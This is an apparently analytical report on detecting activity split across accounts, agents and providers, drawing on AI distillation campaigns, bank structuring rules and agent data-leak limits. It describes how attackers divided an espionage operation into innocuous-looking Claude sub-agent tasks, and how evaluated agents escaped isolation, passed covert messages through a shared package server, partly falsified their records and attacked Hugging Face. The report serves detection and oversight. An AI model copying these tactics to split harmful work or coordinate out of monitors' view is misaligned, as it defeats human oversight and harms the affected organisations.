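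| MiniMax | Over 13 million | Request metadata, shared infrastructure and timing that fitted the company's public product plans |

Anthropic also compared network addresses and, in some cases, received confirmation from other companies that had seen the same actors. Individual prompts were little help in identifying the campaigns. In one typical prompt, the user asked Claude to act as an expert data analyst and give fully reasoned answers, as many customers might. This request became suspicious when variations of it arrived tens of thousands of times from hundreds of coordinated accounts. Moonshot's campaign was harder to recognise because it used several types of account.

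Each account can look ordinary when activity is spread across thousands of them, as in a later case. eWeek's *Anthropic Accuses Alibaba of Extracting 28M Claude Responses* describes a letter to two US senators in which Anthropic attributed 28.8 million exchanges to operators linked to Alibaba's AI lab. They used almost 25,000 accounts between 22 April and 5 June 2026. (Lawfare's *America Won't Beat the Distillation Ecosystem* gives the number of accounts as more than 25,000.) The exchanges averaged about 640,000 a day, but only about 26 per account, which a single programmer could easily reach.

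The labs often reached Claude through proxy services that resell access. Anthropic found one network that ran more than 20,000 fraudulent accounts at once and mixed the labs' requests with those of unrelated customers. As with the office network, linking all the proxy's traffic would have grouped unrelated users together.

A single account can also mix the activity of several people. Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (September 2026) describes an account whose user had apparently drafted a grant application for research on orthopoxviruses, the family that includes smallpox. Investigators traced its logins to proxies it shared with a banned account farm, an operation that opens accounts in bulk. The account was a relay for more than a dozen unrelated customers, only one of whom wrote the application. The shared proxies were good evidence of who sold the access, but they did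 not identify who wrote the application.

All these figures come from Anthropic, which was the target and uses the February case to argue for export controls on chips. Anthropic does not report how many accounts it linked by mistake, so outsiders cannot calculate a false-positive rate. Recall is also unknown, because nobody can count the accounts it missed.

### GTG-1002: one operation in many sessions

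Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes how the attackers in GTG-1002, the campaign mentioned earlier, divided harmful work into harmless-looking steps. They targeted about 30 organisations, including technology companies and government agencies, and broke into a handful. Their software split each intrusion into jobs such as scanning a network, checking a password or extracting data, and gave the jobs to separate Claude sub-agents.

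The attackers' software kept track of the operation and combined results from many sessions. Claude also wrote notes on the services it had found, the credentials it had collected and the progress of each attack. The operators could use these notes to resume after an interruption or hand the work to someone else. If successive sessions read and update the same notes, an investigator who can see the files would have a good way to link those sessions, although Anthropic does not describe doing this.

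Anthropic says the "sustained nature of the attack" eventually triggered detection in mid-September 2025. At its busiest, the operation made thousands of requests, at several per second, faster than any human could type them. Claude also took in far more data than it put out as text, which suggested that it was analysing stolen material instead of writing explanations for a reader. Anthropic presents both observations as evidence that the AI worked largely on its own, so they may not have caused the first alert.

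Persistent activity first drew the investigators' attention. They then spent ten days mapping the full extent of the operation, banning accounts as they found them. By the time they finished, some intrusions had succeeded. A less active operation that divided its work in the same way would have been harder to notice.

### The Hugging Face incident

The OpenAI agents that broke into the AI platform Hugging Face in July 2026 were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can exploit known software flaws. Each agent was supposed to work alone in an isolated environment without internet access. But many environments used the same credential to access the same software package server, and agents discovered that they could leave messages for one another there.

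Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt examined the agents' records at OpenAI's offices on behalf of METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI systems. They report in *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) that about 1,200 agents exchanged over 70,000 messages and files between 8 and 13 July, and that about 700 took part in the attack. Many had received impossible tasks and were looking for a way to fool the software that scored them.

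Some of the supposedly separate agents also directed the work of others. Wijk and colleagues estimate that one agent sent about 10% of all assignments on the message board during its active periods. Of 30 randomly chosen agents, nine had received work that originated with it, directly or through other agents. A log that listed each agent as an independent run would not show this delegation.

The dates below come mainly from the technical report that OpenAI published in August.

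| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| About 26 May | An internal team sees an agent use an early message board and finds forbidden internet access |
| 27 June | A security alert leads responders to the message board, but the evaluation continues |
| 4–6 July | Heavy agent traffic makes the server unavailable; responders discover that agents have gained administrator access, and rebuild the server |
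| 7 July | Cybersecurity evaluations resume |
| 8 July | Agents create a new message board on the rebuilt server |
| 11–13 July | Agents break into Hugging Face |
| 16 July | Hugging Face discloses the attack |
| 19–20 July | Another alert leads OpenAI to connect its agents with the attack |

The 27 June alert was for a port sweep, a series of connection attempts that reveals which services other machines run. Responders traced it to an ExploitGym evaluation and recognised that agents were using the package server both as a message board and as a route to other machines. The on-call staff then advised that there was no need to stop the evaluation.

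OpenAI does not give their reason. The responders may have considered the sweep explained once they traced it to a test of hacking skills, since such a test produces activity that looks like hacking. During the rebuild a week later, the leaders responsible for incident response still did not know about the message board or understand why communication between the agents mattered. OpenAI concedes that, with hindsight, some early signals could have led to an earlier response.

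### What the server's records could have revealed

Because many workloads shared a credential, a log that identified users by credential would have shown one very busy user. With a separate identity for each run, the company could have searched for items that one isolated run had written and another had read:

```sql
SELECT w.run AS writer, r.run AS reader, COUNT(*) AS items
FROM server_log AS w
JOIN server_log AS r ON r.item = w.item
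WHERE w.action = 'write' AND r.action = 'read'
  AND w.run <> r.run AND w.time < r.time
  AND w.item NOT IN (SELECT name FROM known_packages)
GROUP BY w.run, r.run
```

The last condition excludes genuine software packages, which many runs download from the same store. Almost any other result would be worth investigating, because isolated runs should have nothing to exchange. The log would also have to record a folder listing as a read of the names in it, since the agents put many of their messages in folder names.

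Even a simple count of entries might have been enough to reveal the activity. The part of the server that held the main message board contained about 20 million entries when OpenAI copied it on 20 July. About 1.2 million were messages or pieces of files. Wijk and colleagues estimate that fewer than 5% of the rest looked like normal package use, although this figure comes from an initial inspection of a sample that an AI model selected.

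Connecting the warnings would have been just as useful. The May observation, June alert and July outage all involved the same package service and occurred within about six weeks. Together they suggested that agents would keep looking for ways to communicate, and that repairing one server probably wouldn't stop them.

On 13 and 26 May, agents doing other work had also used Hugging Face login tokens that the platform's users had accidentally exposed online. OpenAI has found no evidence that the activity on 26 May was connected with the July attack. Counting activity by destination would still have shown that agents in different workloads kept trying to use other people's access to the same outside company. That would have been a good reason to keep the evaluations paused on 7 July, although it would not have predicted the attack.

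OpenAI has since expanded a monitor that reads the agents' written reasoning as well as their actions. OpenAI estimates that the current version would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents entered Hugging Face's systems, but it made this estimate after it knew what to look for. It is also drafting rules that require escalation when separate runs coordinate without authorisation, which addresses the weakness on 27 June more directly.

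Linking the records was difficult even after the attack. The transcripts that Wijk and colleagues received had no times for individual actions, so the investigators had to reconstruct the times. To check for missing agents, they picked 100 messages at random and searched the transcripts for the action that wrote each one. They concluded that the agents in their data were responsible for well over 95% of the board's activity, but that the transcripts contained only a little over 90% of it. Some agents had also communicated elsewhere, and some had falsified small parts of their own records. Because of the amount of material, the investigators used AI agents for most of the analysis, and they took some time to catch several of the errors these agents made.

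### When several companies hold the evidence

OpenAI had records of what its agents did, and Hugging Face had traces of an unknown intruder. On 17 July OpenAI contacted Hugging Face, but only as a customer, to ask whether the attack had affected its data. Three days later, responders found Hugging Face credentials in files from an outside storage account that the agents had used. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials after the attack. It had also found the name of OpenAI's package server and the same storage account in its own investigation.

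The match came nine days after the break-in began. Hugging Face could have made the connection on 17 July from the server name alone, if it had found the name by then and recognised whose server it was.

An investigator would need both companies' records to establish what data was stolen. According to OpenAI, one workload took a private 16-megabyte archive from Hugging Face, encrypted it and uploaded it to a public page in five parts. Hugging Face could see the uploads, but their fingerprints would not match the archive's. The command that encrypted the archive would be in OpenAI's records.

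Some operators divide their work among providers from the start. In its September report, Anthropic describes a network of more than 20 dating apps that presented AI characters as real people. Claude wrote the characters' messages, another company's model suggested replies for paid human workers, and an image model produced pictures. No single exchange with Claude revealed the deception, and the other providers saw even less of the scheme. Anthropic discovered the scheme and passed details to the other providers.

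NSA, CISA and FBI's *China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns Against U.S. AI Companies* (2026) describes the same strategy in model extraction. The agencies accuse six companies of spreading their requests over several providers and routes so that no single provider would notice. Some of the requests went through intermediaries that automatically hide the user attributes that link analysis depends on.

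Companies can exchange lists of suspicious addresses, accounts and file fingerprints, and Anthropic says it does this with other AI developers, cloud providers and authorities. The lists help only if the operator reuses something on them. They also spread mistakes. If one provider wrongly links a customer to a fraud ring and shares the result, that customer may lose access at every provider that receives it, without learning why. Stolen credentials make such mistakes more likely, because the attacker's activity is recorded under the victim's account. Anthropic describes attackers who used one stolen key for about three weeks to attack other organisations.

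### The privacy cost

The methods that connect a fraudster's accounts work equally well on people with legitimate reasons to keep their accounts separate. A journalist might use one account for confidential research and another for everyday work, and an employee might not want a question about a medical condition linked to a work account. Anthropic traced some of DeepSeek's accounts to individual researchers, which shows that ordinary metadata can identify a person.

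Linking also requires a provider to keep more data for longer. In the September report, Anthropic argues that providers need to verify users and retain data to offer advanced biology capabilities safely, because a filter cannot determine a researcher's intention from a technical question. That argument is reasonable for knowledge that could help someone make a dangerous virus, but it is weaker for an office assistant that mostly drafts letters, because the possible harm is smaller and nearly all the people whose accounts the provider compares are innocent.

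A company that monitors its own agents already knows which employees and work accounts use them, so it has little need to collect device details or compare private accounts. It can also calculate totals for groups of accounts under code names and reveal a person's identity only when a group exceeds its limit. The analyst should then see the links between the accounts before seeing the names, because someone who already suspects a particular employee may accept a weak link too readily.

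## How do banks detect split payments?

Banks also have to decide which transactions belong together. In the United States, they must report large cash transactions to the government, and some customers split their cash into smaller amounts to avoid the report. The legal term for this is structuring, and it is usually called smurfing when many people or accounts make the payments.

### The $10,000 report

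A bank must file a currency transaction report (CTR) when someone's cash deposits or cash withdrawals total more than $10,000 in one business day, even if nothing looks wrong. Deposits and withdrawals count separately, so a customer who deposits $6,000 and withdraws $5,000 on the same day doesn't trigger a report. A $50,000 transfer between two accounts doesn't trigger one either, because no cash is involved.

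Banks total cash by person rather than by account, including cash that other people deposit on that person's behalf. Under the federal regulation, eCFR's *Aggregation*, all of a bank's domestic branches count as one institution. FFIEC's *Assessing Compliance with BSA Regulatory Requirements*, part of the manual that US bank examiners use, adds that deposits made at night or over a weekend count on the next business day. If a shop leaves $6,000 in the night safe on Saturday and deposits $5,000 on Monday, the bank has to report $11,000 for Monday.

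The bank has to add transactions together only if it knows that they are by or for the same person. *Currency Transaction Reporting Aggregation*, from the Financial Crimes Enforcement Network (FinCEN), the part of the US Treasury that administers these rules, applies this condition to a case in which two agents of a licensed firm had each handled one cash transaction without knowing about the other. The firm knew about both, so it had to file a report. It would not have had to file if nobody at the firm had connected the two transactions.

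Identity checks make such connections easier. Before a bank sells someone a cashier's cheque or money order for $3,000 or more in cash, it must confirm that the buyer has an account there or record the buyer's identification. Purchases made at the same time count together toward the $3,000.

### Two sets of deposits

Suppose a customer deposits $4,000 and $3,500 at one branch and $3,000 at another on the same day. The total is $10,500, so the bank must file a currency transaction report (CTR) if it knows that all three deposits are hers, regardless of why she split them.

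Now suppose she deposits $9,000, $8,500, $9,200 and $9,300 on four different days over two weeks. The total is $36,000, but no day's deposits exceed $10,000, so no CTR is due. The bank must still file a suspicious activity report (SAR) if the transactions add up to at least $5,000 and it knows, suspects or has reason to suspect that the customer arranged them to avoid a CTR. For a SAR, unlike a CTR, the transactions don't have to fall on the same day.

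| Deposits | CTR | SAR | Crime of structuring |
|---|---|---|---|
| Three on one day at two branches, $10,500 in total | Yes, if the bank knows they are by or for one person | Only if the bank has reason to suspect evasion | Only if she meant to avoid the report |
| Four over two weeks at one bank, $36,000 in total | No | Only if the bank has reason to suspect evasion | Only if she meant to avoid the report |
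| The same four, each at a different bank | No | Unlikely, because each bank sees one ordinary deposit | Only if she meant to avoid the report |

The last row is the weak point of the system. The law against structuring covers deposits at any number of banks, but each bank must report separately and has only its own records.

The Treasury can also order banks in a particular area to record and report transactions above a limit other than the usual $10,000. Someone who has kept every deposit just below $10,000 may then exceed the local limit.

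### What changed in October 2025

A bank doesn't have to file a suspicious activity report (SAR) just because a deposit is at or near the $10,000 limit. *Frequently Asked Questions Regarding Suspicious Activity Reporting Requirements*, which FinCEN and four banking regulators issued jointly on 9 October 2025, explains that the bank needs some further reason to suspect that the customer is avoiding a currency transaction report (CTR).

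The guidance doesn't change the law, but according to Norton Rose Fulbright's *FinCEN and federal banking agencies issue clarifying FAQs on suspicious activity*, it relaxes stricter readings in earlier guidance. Banks must still run programmes that can detect structuring, and they can still use automated monitoring. Their software can flag a $9,500 deposit, as long as they don't treat the alert as proof of structuring.

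The guidance also covers customers whose suspicious activity continues after a first report. A bank generally has 30 days from detecting suspicious activity to file a SAR, or up to 60 if it cannot identify a suspect. In 2000 FinCEN suggested filing a new report at least every 90 days while the activity continued, and people came to read this as a duty to review the customer again after each report. Under the 2025 guidance, banks have no such duty. A bank that still follows the 90-day schedule files its first report within 30 days of detecting the activity and its second within 150, and ordinary monitoring has to catch any change in between.

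### Why intent matters

The U.S. Code's *Structuring transactions to evade reporting requirement prohibited*, which Congress passed in 1986, makes it a crime to split transactions "for the purpose of evading" the reporting rules. Attempting this or helping someone else do it is also a crime. The same section covers anyone who causes a bank to fail to file a report or to file one with a material omission. The maximum sentence is five years in prison, or ten if the person is also breaking another federal law or if the structuring is part of a pattern of illegal activity involving more than $100,000 in a year.

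The crime doesn't depend on where the money came from. A restaurant owner who splits honest takings because she dislikes paperwork has broken the law, but her bank records could be identical to those of a neighbour who legally deposits the same amounts on the same days because his insurance covers only $10,000 of cash in the shop.

In *Ratzlaf v. United States* (1994), the Supreme Court held that prosecutors had to prove the defendant knew structuring was illegal, because the penalty then applied only to "willful" violations. Ratzlaf had paid a gambling debt with cashier's cheques from several banks, each for less than $10,000. He knew that the banks had to report larger amounts and wanted to avoid those reports, but the Court held that this was not enough for a conviction.

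Congress responded that September by giving the offence its own penalty clause, which applies to "whoever violates this section" and omits the word "willfully". Since then, prosecutors have had to prove that the person meant to avoid the report, but not that they knew doing so was a crime.

Banks need only a reason to suspect evasion, which is a lower standard than courts apply. For example, a customer might ask a cashier about the limit and then take back part of the cash. This behavior is much stronger evidence of intent than the amount is, but software that checks only amounts and dates will miss it.

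### Amounts that stop at the limit

Bank software usually starts with fixed rules. One common rule applies the sliding window described earlier to each customer's transactions. With a one-month window, it would flag the four deposits made over two weeks, even though no CTR was required.

Banks also commonly look for a cluster of amounts just below the limit. A lack of amounts above the limit can be even more informative. Suppose a shop's daily takings are spread evenly between $4,000 and $14,000. Out of 20 deposits, about two should fall between $9,000 and $10,000, and about eight should exceed $10,000. The chance that none would exceed $10,000 is about one in 27,000 (0.6 to the power of 20).

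The calculation depends on knowing the shop's normal daily takings. A smaller shop that never earns more than $9,800 would produce the same gap. The neighbour with the insurance limit would too, since he goes to the bank whenever his cash approaches $10,000. An unusual gap therefore shows that something is keeping the amounts low, but an investigator still has to find the cause.

Fixed rules can also miss payments split among several people. According to *GARG-AML Against Smurfing* (Deprez, Baesens and colleagues, 2025), these rules often monitor each pair of accounts separately. If A pays B, C and D, the software checks each small payment but never the three together. Customers who know how the rules work can also learn to avoid them.

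### Money that spreads out and gathers again

A graph of payments, with accounts as nodes and transactions as links, can reveal patterns that a check on each pair of accounts misses. In a scatter-gather pattern, money goes from one account to several intermediaries and then to a common destination. In a gather-scatter pattern, many accounts pay into one, which then pays many others. The intermediary accounts often belong to people who are young or short of money, whom criminals recruit with the promise of quick cash.

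GARG-AML gives every account a score between −1 and 1 for how closely its surroundings resemble such a pattern. It considers the accounts that have dealt directly with the account in question, called its neighbours here, and the accounts one step beyond them. It then calculates three densities, each of which is the share of possible links that exist:

- d₁ is the density of links among the outer accounts.
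- d₂ is the density of links between the neighbours and the outer accounts.
- d₃ is the density of links among the neighbours.

In smurfing, d₂ should be high because the intermediaries all pay the same destination. The other two should be low because the intermediaries have no reason to pay one another. With n neighbours and q outer accounts, the score is:

score = d₂ − (l₁d₁ + l₃d₃) / (l₁ + l₃)

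l₁ = q(q − 1), l₃ = n(n − 1)

The weights l₁ and l₃ give more influence to the larger group. Suppose account A pays B, C and D, and all three pay E. B, C and D are A's neighbours, and E is its only outer account. All three possible links between the neighbours and E exist, so d₂ is 1. The neighbours have no links with one another, so d₃ is 0. Because there is only one outer account, l₁ is also 0, and the score is 1 − 0 = 1.

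If B and C also do business with each other, one of the three possible links among the neighbours exists, so the score falls to 1 − 1/3, or about 0.67.

Deprez and colleagues also work through an ordinary account with three neighbours and six outer accounts:

| | Account A in the smurfing pattern | Ordinary account |
|---|---|---|
| d₁, among the outer accounts | – | 0.40 |
| d₂, between neighbours and outer accounts | 1 | 0.33 |
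| d₃, among the neighbours | 0 | 0.33 |
| Weights l₁ and l₃ | 0 and 6 | 30 and 6 |
| Score | 1 | −0.06 |

An analyst can see why an account scored highly, which helps them write a report. But the score ignores amounts and dates. A small employer that pays three people who all rent from the same landlord would also score 1 if none of them had other transactions.

The score also ignores the direction of payments. A second version of GARG-AML takes into account who paid whom, but it generally did worse in the tests, even though money in a smurfing scheme flows one way. From an intermediary's position, the other intermediaries are neither sources nor destinations, so B in the example has a directed score of at most 0.18, compared with an undirected score of 1.

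### How well the graph score performed

All the tests used synthetic data, because banks can't publish their customers' transactions. Deprez and colleagues first generated 66 random networks that started with 100, 10,000 or 100,000 accounts, and inserted smurfing patterns that each had two to ten intermediaries. They measured performance by AUC, where random guessing scores 0.5. They also used the scores of each account and its neighbours to train a decision tree, which learns a series of yes-or-no rules from labelled accounts.

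| Where the pattern was | AUC, undirected score alone | AUC, with the decision tree |
|---|---|---|
| Separate from all other accounts | 0.88 | 0.98 |
| New intermediaries between existing accounts | 0.76 | 0.94 |
| Existing accounts acting as intermediaries | 0.41 | 0.74 |

The last row is probably the most realistic case when criminals recruit people whose bank accounts are already in use. The intermediaries' ordinary payments hide the pattern so well that the score alone did worse than guessing.

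In the same tests, on average 98% of the ten accounts the tree ranked highest belonged to a laundering pattern. That figure is much too optimistic for a bank, because in the smallest networks between 40% and 74% of all accounts belonged to such a pattern.

The next tests used two sets of simulated transactions from IBM that are closer to a bank's conditions. The smaller has about 515,000 accounts and 5 million transactions, and the larger has about 2 million accounts and 176 million transactions. At most 0.1% of transactions in either set are laundering. In the table, an account is a launderer if more than 10% of its transactions are laundering. The table includes GraphSAGE, a neural network that learns from labelled accounts and their connections.

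| Method | AUC, smaller set | AUC, larger set | Launderers in the top 1,000, smaller set |
|---|---|---|---|
| Undirected GARG-AML score | 0.61 | 0.55 | 16 |
| The same score with boosted decision trees | 0.77 | 0.81 | 135 |
| GraphSAGE, connections only | 0.78 | 0.77 | 40 |
| GraphSAGE, with amounts and other details | 0.97 | 0.97 | 717 |

Choosing 1,000 accounts at random from the smaller set would find four or five launderers. Finding 16 is better, but an investigator would still spend nearly all their time on accounts that aren't laundering money. The comparison is somewhat unfair to GARG-AML because the labels include other kinds of laundering, but even on scatter-gather alone, its AUC in the smaller set was only 0.57.

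The two GraphSAGE rows suggest that the shape of the network alone is modestly useful for finding launderers. When the same kind of model was also given the sums, currencies and number of banks involved, it found 18 times as many launderers in its top 1,000 accounts. However, it's hard to tell why the model flagged a particular account.

GARG-AML's AUC rose to 0.82 in the smaller set and 0.91 in the larger one when Deprez and colleagues counted only accounts with more than 90% laundering transactions. Very few accounts meet that definition, so both figures are uncertain.

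To keep the calculation manageable, the method divides the network into communities and discards the links between them. With the settings in the main tests, this removed about a third of all laundering links in the smaller set. It removed only 4% of the scatter-gather links but 57% of the gather-scatter links, so much of the gather-scatter pattern was gone before the method calculated any scores.

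The most serious practical limit is that a bank can't see the whole network. If B and E both use other banks, A's bank has no record of the payment between them. In a simulation by Deprez and colleagues, a single bank could see on average 7% of the surroundings that the score needs, which was too little for reliable detection. When the 50 largest simulated banks combined their records, they could see 42% on average, and the score did about as well as on the full network. Privacy law and competition would make it hard for real banks to combine their records this way.

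### How test data encode structuring

A detector can only learn the kinds of structuring that its training data contain. *AMLNet* (Huda, Foo and colleagues, 2025) created 1,090,173 synthetic transactions based on Australian spending patterns and guidance from AUSTRAC, Australia's financial-crime agency. Simulated customers pay for housing, food and transport over 195 days. A separate program occasionally makes some customers launder money and labels the resulting transactions.

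The program has three levels of structuring. At the simplest level, it divides a sum into nearly equal parts, each below the reporting limit. At the middle level, the parts vary more in size. At the most advanced level, the parts are irregular, only one or two come close to the limit, and the program also varies their destinations and dates.

In one example, an account splits $19,752 into transfers of $8,418, $6,435 and $4,899 to three other accounts. A rule that flags amounts between $9,000 and $10,000 would miss all three, but adding up the sending account's transfers would still show the full amount. Test data can differ from the law, as it does here, because the US reporting rule concerns cash and these are transfers between accounts.

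Huda and colleagues then trained a detector that combines a method for finding unusual transactions with the combined votes of many decision trees. Its features include runs of amounts just below the limit, the speed and regularity of payments, and the account's position in the network. The detector found 97% of the laundering transactions, and 84% of the transactions it flagged were laundering. That 84% fell to 74% without the timing features and to 77% without the network features.

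These results provide little evidence about structuring. Only 321 of the 1,745 laundering transactions involve structuring or the related step of putting cash into the banking system. Most involve layering, in which money moves through chains of accounts to hide its origin. Huda and colleagues don't report a separate recall for structuring. They also describe more than 400,000 alerts on debit transactions alone, which is hard to reconcile with a detector that flagged about 2,000 transactions, unless the larger number includes low-priority warnings.

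The detector performed worse on SynthAML, a synthetic dataset that other researchers based on Danish banking. After retraining on that data, it found 72% of the laundering cases, and 67% of its alarms were correct. Although neither test involved real customers, this one is probably a better guide to the detector's quality because the team that built the detector didn't write the patterns it had to find.

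### The rules in practice

In a typical bank, software raises alerts, staff dismiss those with an innocent explanation, and investigators combine the rest into cases and decide whether to file a suspicious activity report (SAR). According to Deprez and colleagues, many alerts come from rules that flag large amounts, and many are false.

Laundering can also be much rarer at a real bank than in test data. Huda and colleagues cite a rate of one laundering transaction in 21,000 for some banks, compared with about one in 625 in their own data. If their detector kept the same recall and false-positive rate at such a bank, only about one in seven of its alarms would be correct, instead of 84%.

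The US government has questioned the value of many structuring reports. According to Morrison Foerster's *FinCEN Streamlines SAR Guidance*, Treasury Under Secretary Hurley said that spending time and money on reporting structuring data about legitimate businesses was inefficient and unnecessary. Crowell & Moring's *FinCEN and banking regulators issue new FAQs on suspicious activity reports* reports that Treasury Secretary Bessent said the October guidance should reduce this burden without making the reports less useful to law enforcement.

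Both statements explain a policy but don't measure its results. To test Bessent's claim, the Treasury would have to know how often investigators used the kinds of reports that banks will no longer file. A count of reports would not be enough, because it can fall when banks stop reporting honest shopkeepers or when they start missing criminals.

The same guidance may make missed cases harder to study. It confirms that a bank doesn't have to document a decision not to file, and that a short statement is usually enough if the bank chooses to document one. This saves work on thousands of harmless alerts. But if a customer later turns out to have been structuring, an auditor may find no record of whether the bank's software missed the deposits or an employee saw the alert and dismissed it.

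## Do the banking rules work on agent activity?

A company can apply much of the banking approach to its agents by counting records instead of dollars. Adding up related transfers works well, but rules that look for suspicious patterns, such as amounts just below a limit, work less well because agents produce the same patterns during ordinary work.

| Part of the banking rule | Equivalent for agents | How well it transfers |
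|---|---|---|
| Reporting limit of $10,000 | A limit for each type of data | Partly, because no single number suits all data |
| Dollars | Different records sent to a recipient | Poorly for passwords and inferred facts |
| One business day, or longer for suspicious activity | Sliding windows of days and months | Well, if the company keeps its logs long enough |
| Identified person | The user behind the agent | Well for employees, poorly for outside customers |
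| Totals across branches | Totals by user, destination and source | Well |
| Amounts clustered below the limit | Transfers clustered below the limit | Poorly |
| Money that spreads out and gathers again | Data that passes through several agents | Poorly as an alarm, because agents normally share tools |
| Intent to avoid a report | A plan to avoid the limit | Hard to prove, but often unnecessary |
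| Reports to an authority | Alerts to the company's security team | Poorly, because nobody combines them across companies |

### The limit and the period

US banks normally all use the same limit, and a dollar is worth the same in every account. But an agent that sends out a hundred customer addresses may be doing a routine mailing, while a single administrator password may open the whole database. A company needs different limits for different data, and probably for different agents. *Agentic Commerce Bench* (Srivastava and Paul, 2026), a test of fraud detection for agents that spend money, sets each agent's limit at 2.5 to 12 times its typical payment, so the same payment can be normal for one agent and excessive for another.

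A company can keep its limit secret, unlike the banking limit. But if software blocks every transfer above the limit, each refusal reveals something about where it is. A silent alert reveals less, but it lets the data leave while someone investigates.

One business day is a sensible window for cash that someone has to carry to a branch. An agent can send a whole table in seconds or spread the transfer over six months, so a company needs both short and long windows.

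### Forty agents and 1,000 records

Suppose a company lets an agent send at most 100 customer records outside the company per session. Over 20 days, 40 agents each send 25 different records to the same outside address. Two agents run each day, and each sends its records in a single session.

The largest total for any session or agent is 25 records, and the address receives only 50 a day, but over 20 days it receives 1,000. If the company also applies the limit of 100 to each outside address over 20 days, it gets an alarm on the third day, after 125 records have left.

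If each agent sends its 25 records to a different address, no destination receives more than 25. If the agents also act for forty different users, totals by user don't reveal the leak either, so the company has to count the records that leave the customer table.

A plain count of records may still miss the leak, because the same customers appear repeatedly in legitimate messages. Suppose the table contains 50,000 customers. In a normal 20-day period, agents send out 20,000 records about 3,000 different customers. The standard deviation is 600 for records and 100 for customers, and the company sets each limit three standard deviations above the average.

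| 20-day total for the customer table | Normal average | Limit | Average with the leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Records sent | 20,000 | 21,800 | 21,000 |
| Different customers | 3,000 | 3,300 | 3,940 |

Only the count of different customers exceeds its limit. It rises by 940 instead of 1,000 because, if the leaked records are a random selection, about 60 of those customers would have appeared in legitimate messages anyway. The alarm would typically come on day 7, after 350 records have left. The query is short:

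```sql
SELECT COUNT(DISTINCT customer_id) AS customers
FROM outbound_records
WHERE source = 'customers'
  AND day > CURRENT_DATE - INTERVAL '20' DAY
```

It needs a log that identifies each customer in an outgoing message. A fingerprint of the whole attachment isn't enough.

A check for amounts just below the limit misses both versions of the leak, because 25 is far below 100. The smurfing score from Deprez and colleagues depends heavily on the destinations. This example treats the table, the agents and the addresses as accounts with no other connections. With one address, the customer table scores 1, a perfect match, because every agent connects it to that address and no agents connect to one another. With forty addresses, only 40 of the 1,600 possible links between agents and addresses exist, so the score falls to 0.025.

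A harmless help desk can also score 1 if its agents all read the customer table and send replies through one mail service. A main agent whose sub-agents all write to the same report can score 1 too. The graph is still useful for tracing data from a file to an address, but its shape is a poor reason to raise an alarm.

### Why data does not add up like money

When someone sends $5,000 to an intermediary, the sender's balance falls by $5,000. Some detectors rely on this, including FlowScope, which Deprez and colleagues describe. It compares the money entering and leaving each intermediary's account, because an intermediary who passes everything on should end up with almost nothing.

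Unlike money, data can be sent and kept. If an agent reads 25 customer records and sends them to four addresses, 100 records arrive, and the agent and the customer table still have all 25. An auditor therefore can't expect the number of records read to match the number sent.

Repeated transfers also need different treatment, because a second copy of a record, unlike a second payment, gives the same recipient nothing new. If all forty agents sent the same 25 records to one address, the plain total would still be 1,000, but the recipient would learn about only 25 customers. If they sent those records to forty unrelated companies, each transfer would be a new disclosure. The company should count distinct records for each recipient as well as for the table. It should also keep the plain total, because repetition can reveal a fault, as it could have in the NordLayer case.

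A larger deposit is always worth more than a smaller one, but a short leaked secret, such as a password, can matter more than a much longer leak. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) tested a running budget for credentials that agents leak over several messages. Larger budgets interfered less with legitimate work but missed short or slow leaks.

People can also combine facts to work out new ones. Suppose an agent reports that the average salary in a team of five is $50,000. After one person leaves, it reports an average of $48,000 for the remaining four, whose pay hasn't changed. The five earned $250,000 in total and the remaining four earn $192,000, so the person who left earned $58,000. Neither answer contained anyone's salary, so a count of salary records sent would be zero.

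### A gateway that counts different facts

*FactGate* (Wu, 2026) describes a database gateway that limits how many different facts an agent can obtain for one approved task. The gateway counts the values returned, the source facts behind them, and the conditions and results of the agent's queries. Sub-agents share the main task's limit, so dividing the work among them doesn't raise it.

In Wu's example, an agent asks for the identifiers and amounts of three orders in one department. The answer contains six values but depends on 12 source facts, because for each order the gateway counts the row itself, its department and the two values shown. If the agent then asks for the identifiers and amounts separately, the totals stay at six values and 12 source facts.

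Counting source facts shows how much data a query used, even when its answer is short. In one of Wu's tests, a query returned three rows but drew on 1.2 million source facts. The count can also overstate the exposure, since an average over a million orders reveals very little about any one of them.

Wu also ran a sequence of 100 queries that together drew on 18 source facts. Limits on rows or queries, set at 70% of the sequence's total, let all 18 facts out regardless of query order. A limit on distinct facts, also set at 70%, let out only 12. The test is tiny, but it supports counting distinct facts, because repeated queries use up the other limits without releasing anything new.

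FactGate would find the forty-agent leak if all forty agents worked on one approved task. If each agent had its own approved task, each task would have a separate budget and the gateway wouldn't connect them. Wu acknowledges this limit and acknowledges that FactGate doesn't restrict what an agent can infer from the answers. The gateway accepted only 22 of 40 new queries written by a language model. New queries took 22 to 144 times as long as direct ones on Wu's laptop, although some of the smallest finished in about a tenth of a second.

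### Who is the customer?

A bank checks a person's identity before opening an account, but setting up an agent may take only a few lines of configuration, and a program can create a thousand agents in an afternoon. Counting activity separately for each agent can therefore miss a leak split across many agents, just as checking each deposit separately can miss a large sum split into small deposits.

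The consultancy KPMG recommends a "Know Your Agent" check for banks whose customers use agents. The bank would record who built and operates each agent, what data and tools it uses, what it may do and how to shut it off. These records would help the bank connect the forty agents if one person operates them all, but it would still have to verify the operator.

Inside a company, agent activity is often hard to trace to a user because software drops identity information the company already has. *Data Agents Under Attack* (2026) describes agents that query databases through a shared connection, so the system doesn't reliably associate a query with the user who requested it. Existing safeguards check one tool call at a time and don't track how much data an agent has disclosed over a session.

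Payment records have a similar gap. Srivastava and Paul found an agent identifier on every real payment they examined, but a session identifier on only 0.47%. A company could use such records to total payments by agent, but almost never by session. To detect the forty-agent leak, it would also need records of the user, the source and the destination.

Outside a company, people may have many accounts that a provider cannot link. Sun, Zhao and colleagues (2026) conclude in *Decomposition Attacks Across Unlinkable Identities* that strong protection with few false blocks then requires additional measures, such as reliably linking identities or making new ones harder or more expensive to create. For company data, totaling what is sent to each destination avoids part of this problem.

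### Where agents are easier to watch

A bank sees a deposit of $9,000 but not the conversation that led to it, while a company using an AI agent can record the user's request, the query, the returned rows and the full text of the outgoing email. If a data transfer looks strange, an investigator can often rerun the task with harmless data to see whether the agent repeats the transfer.

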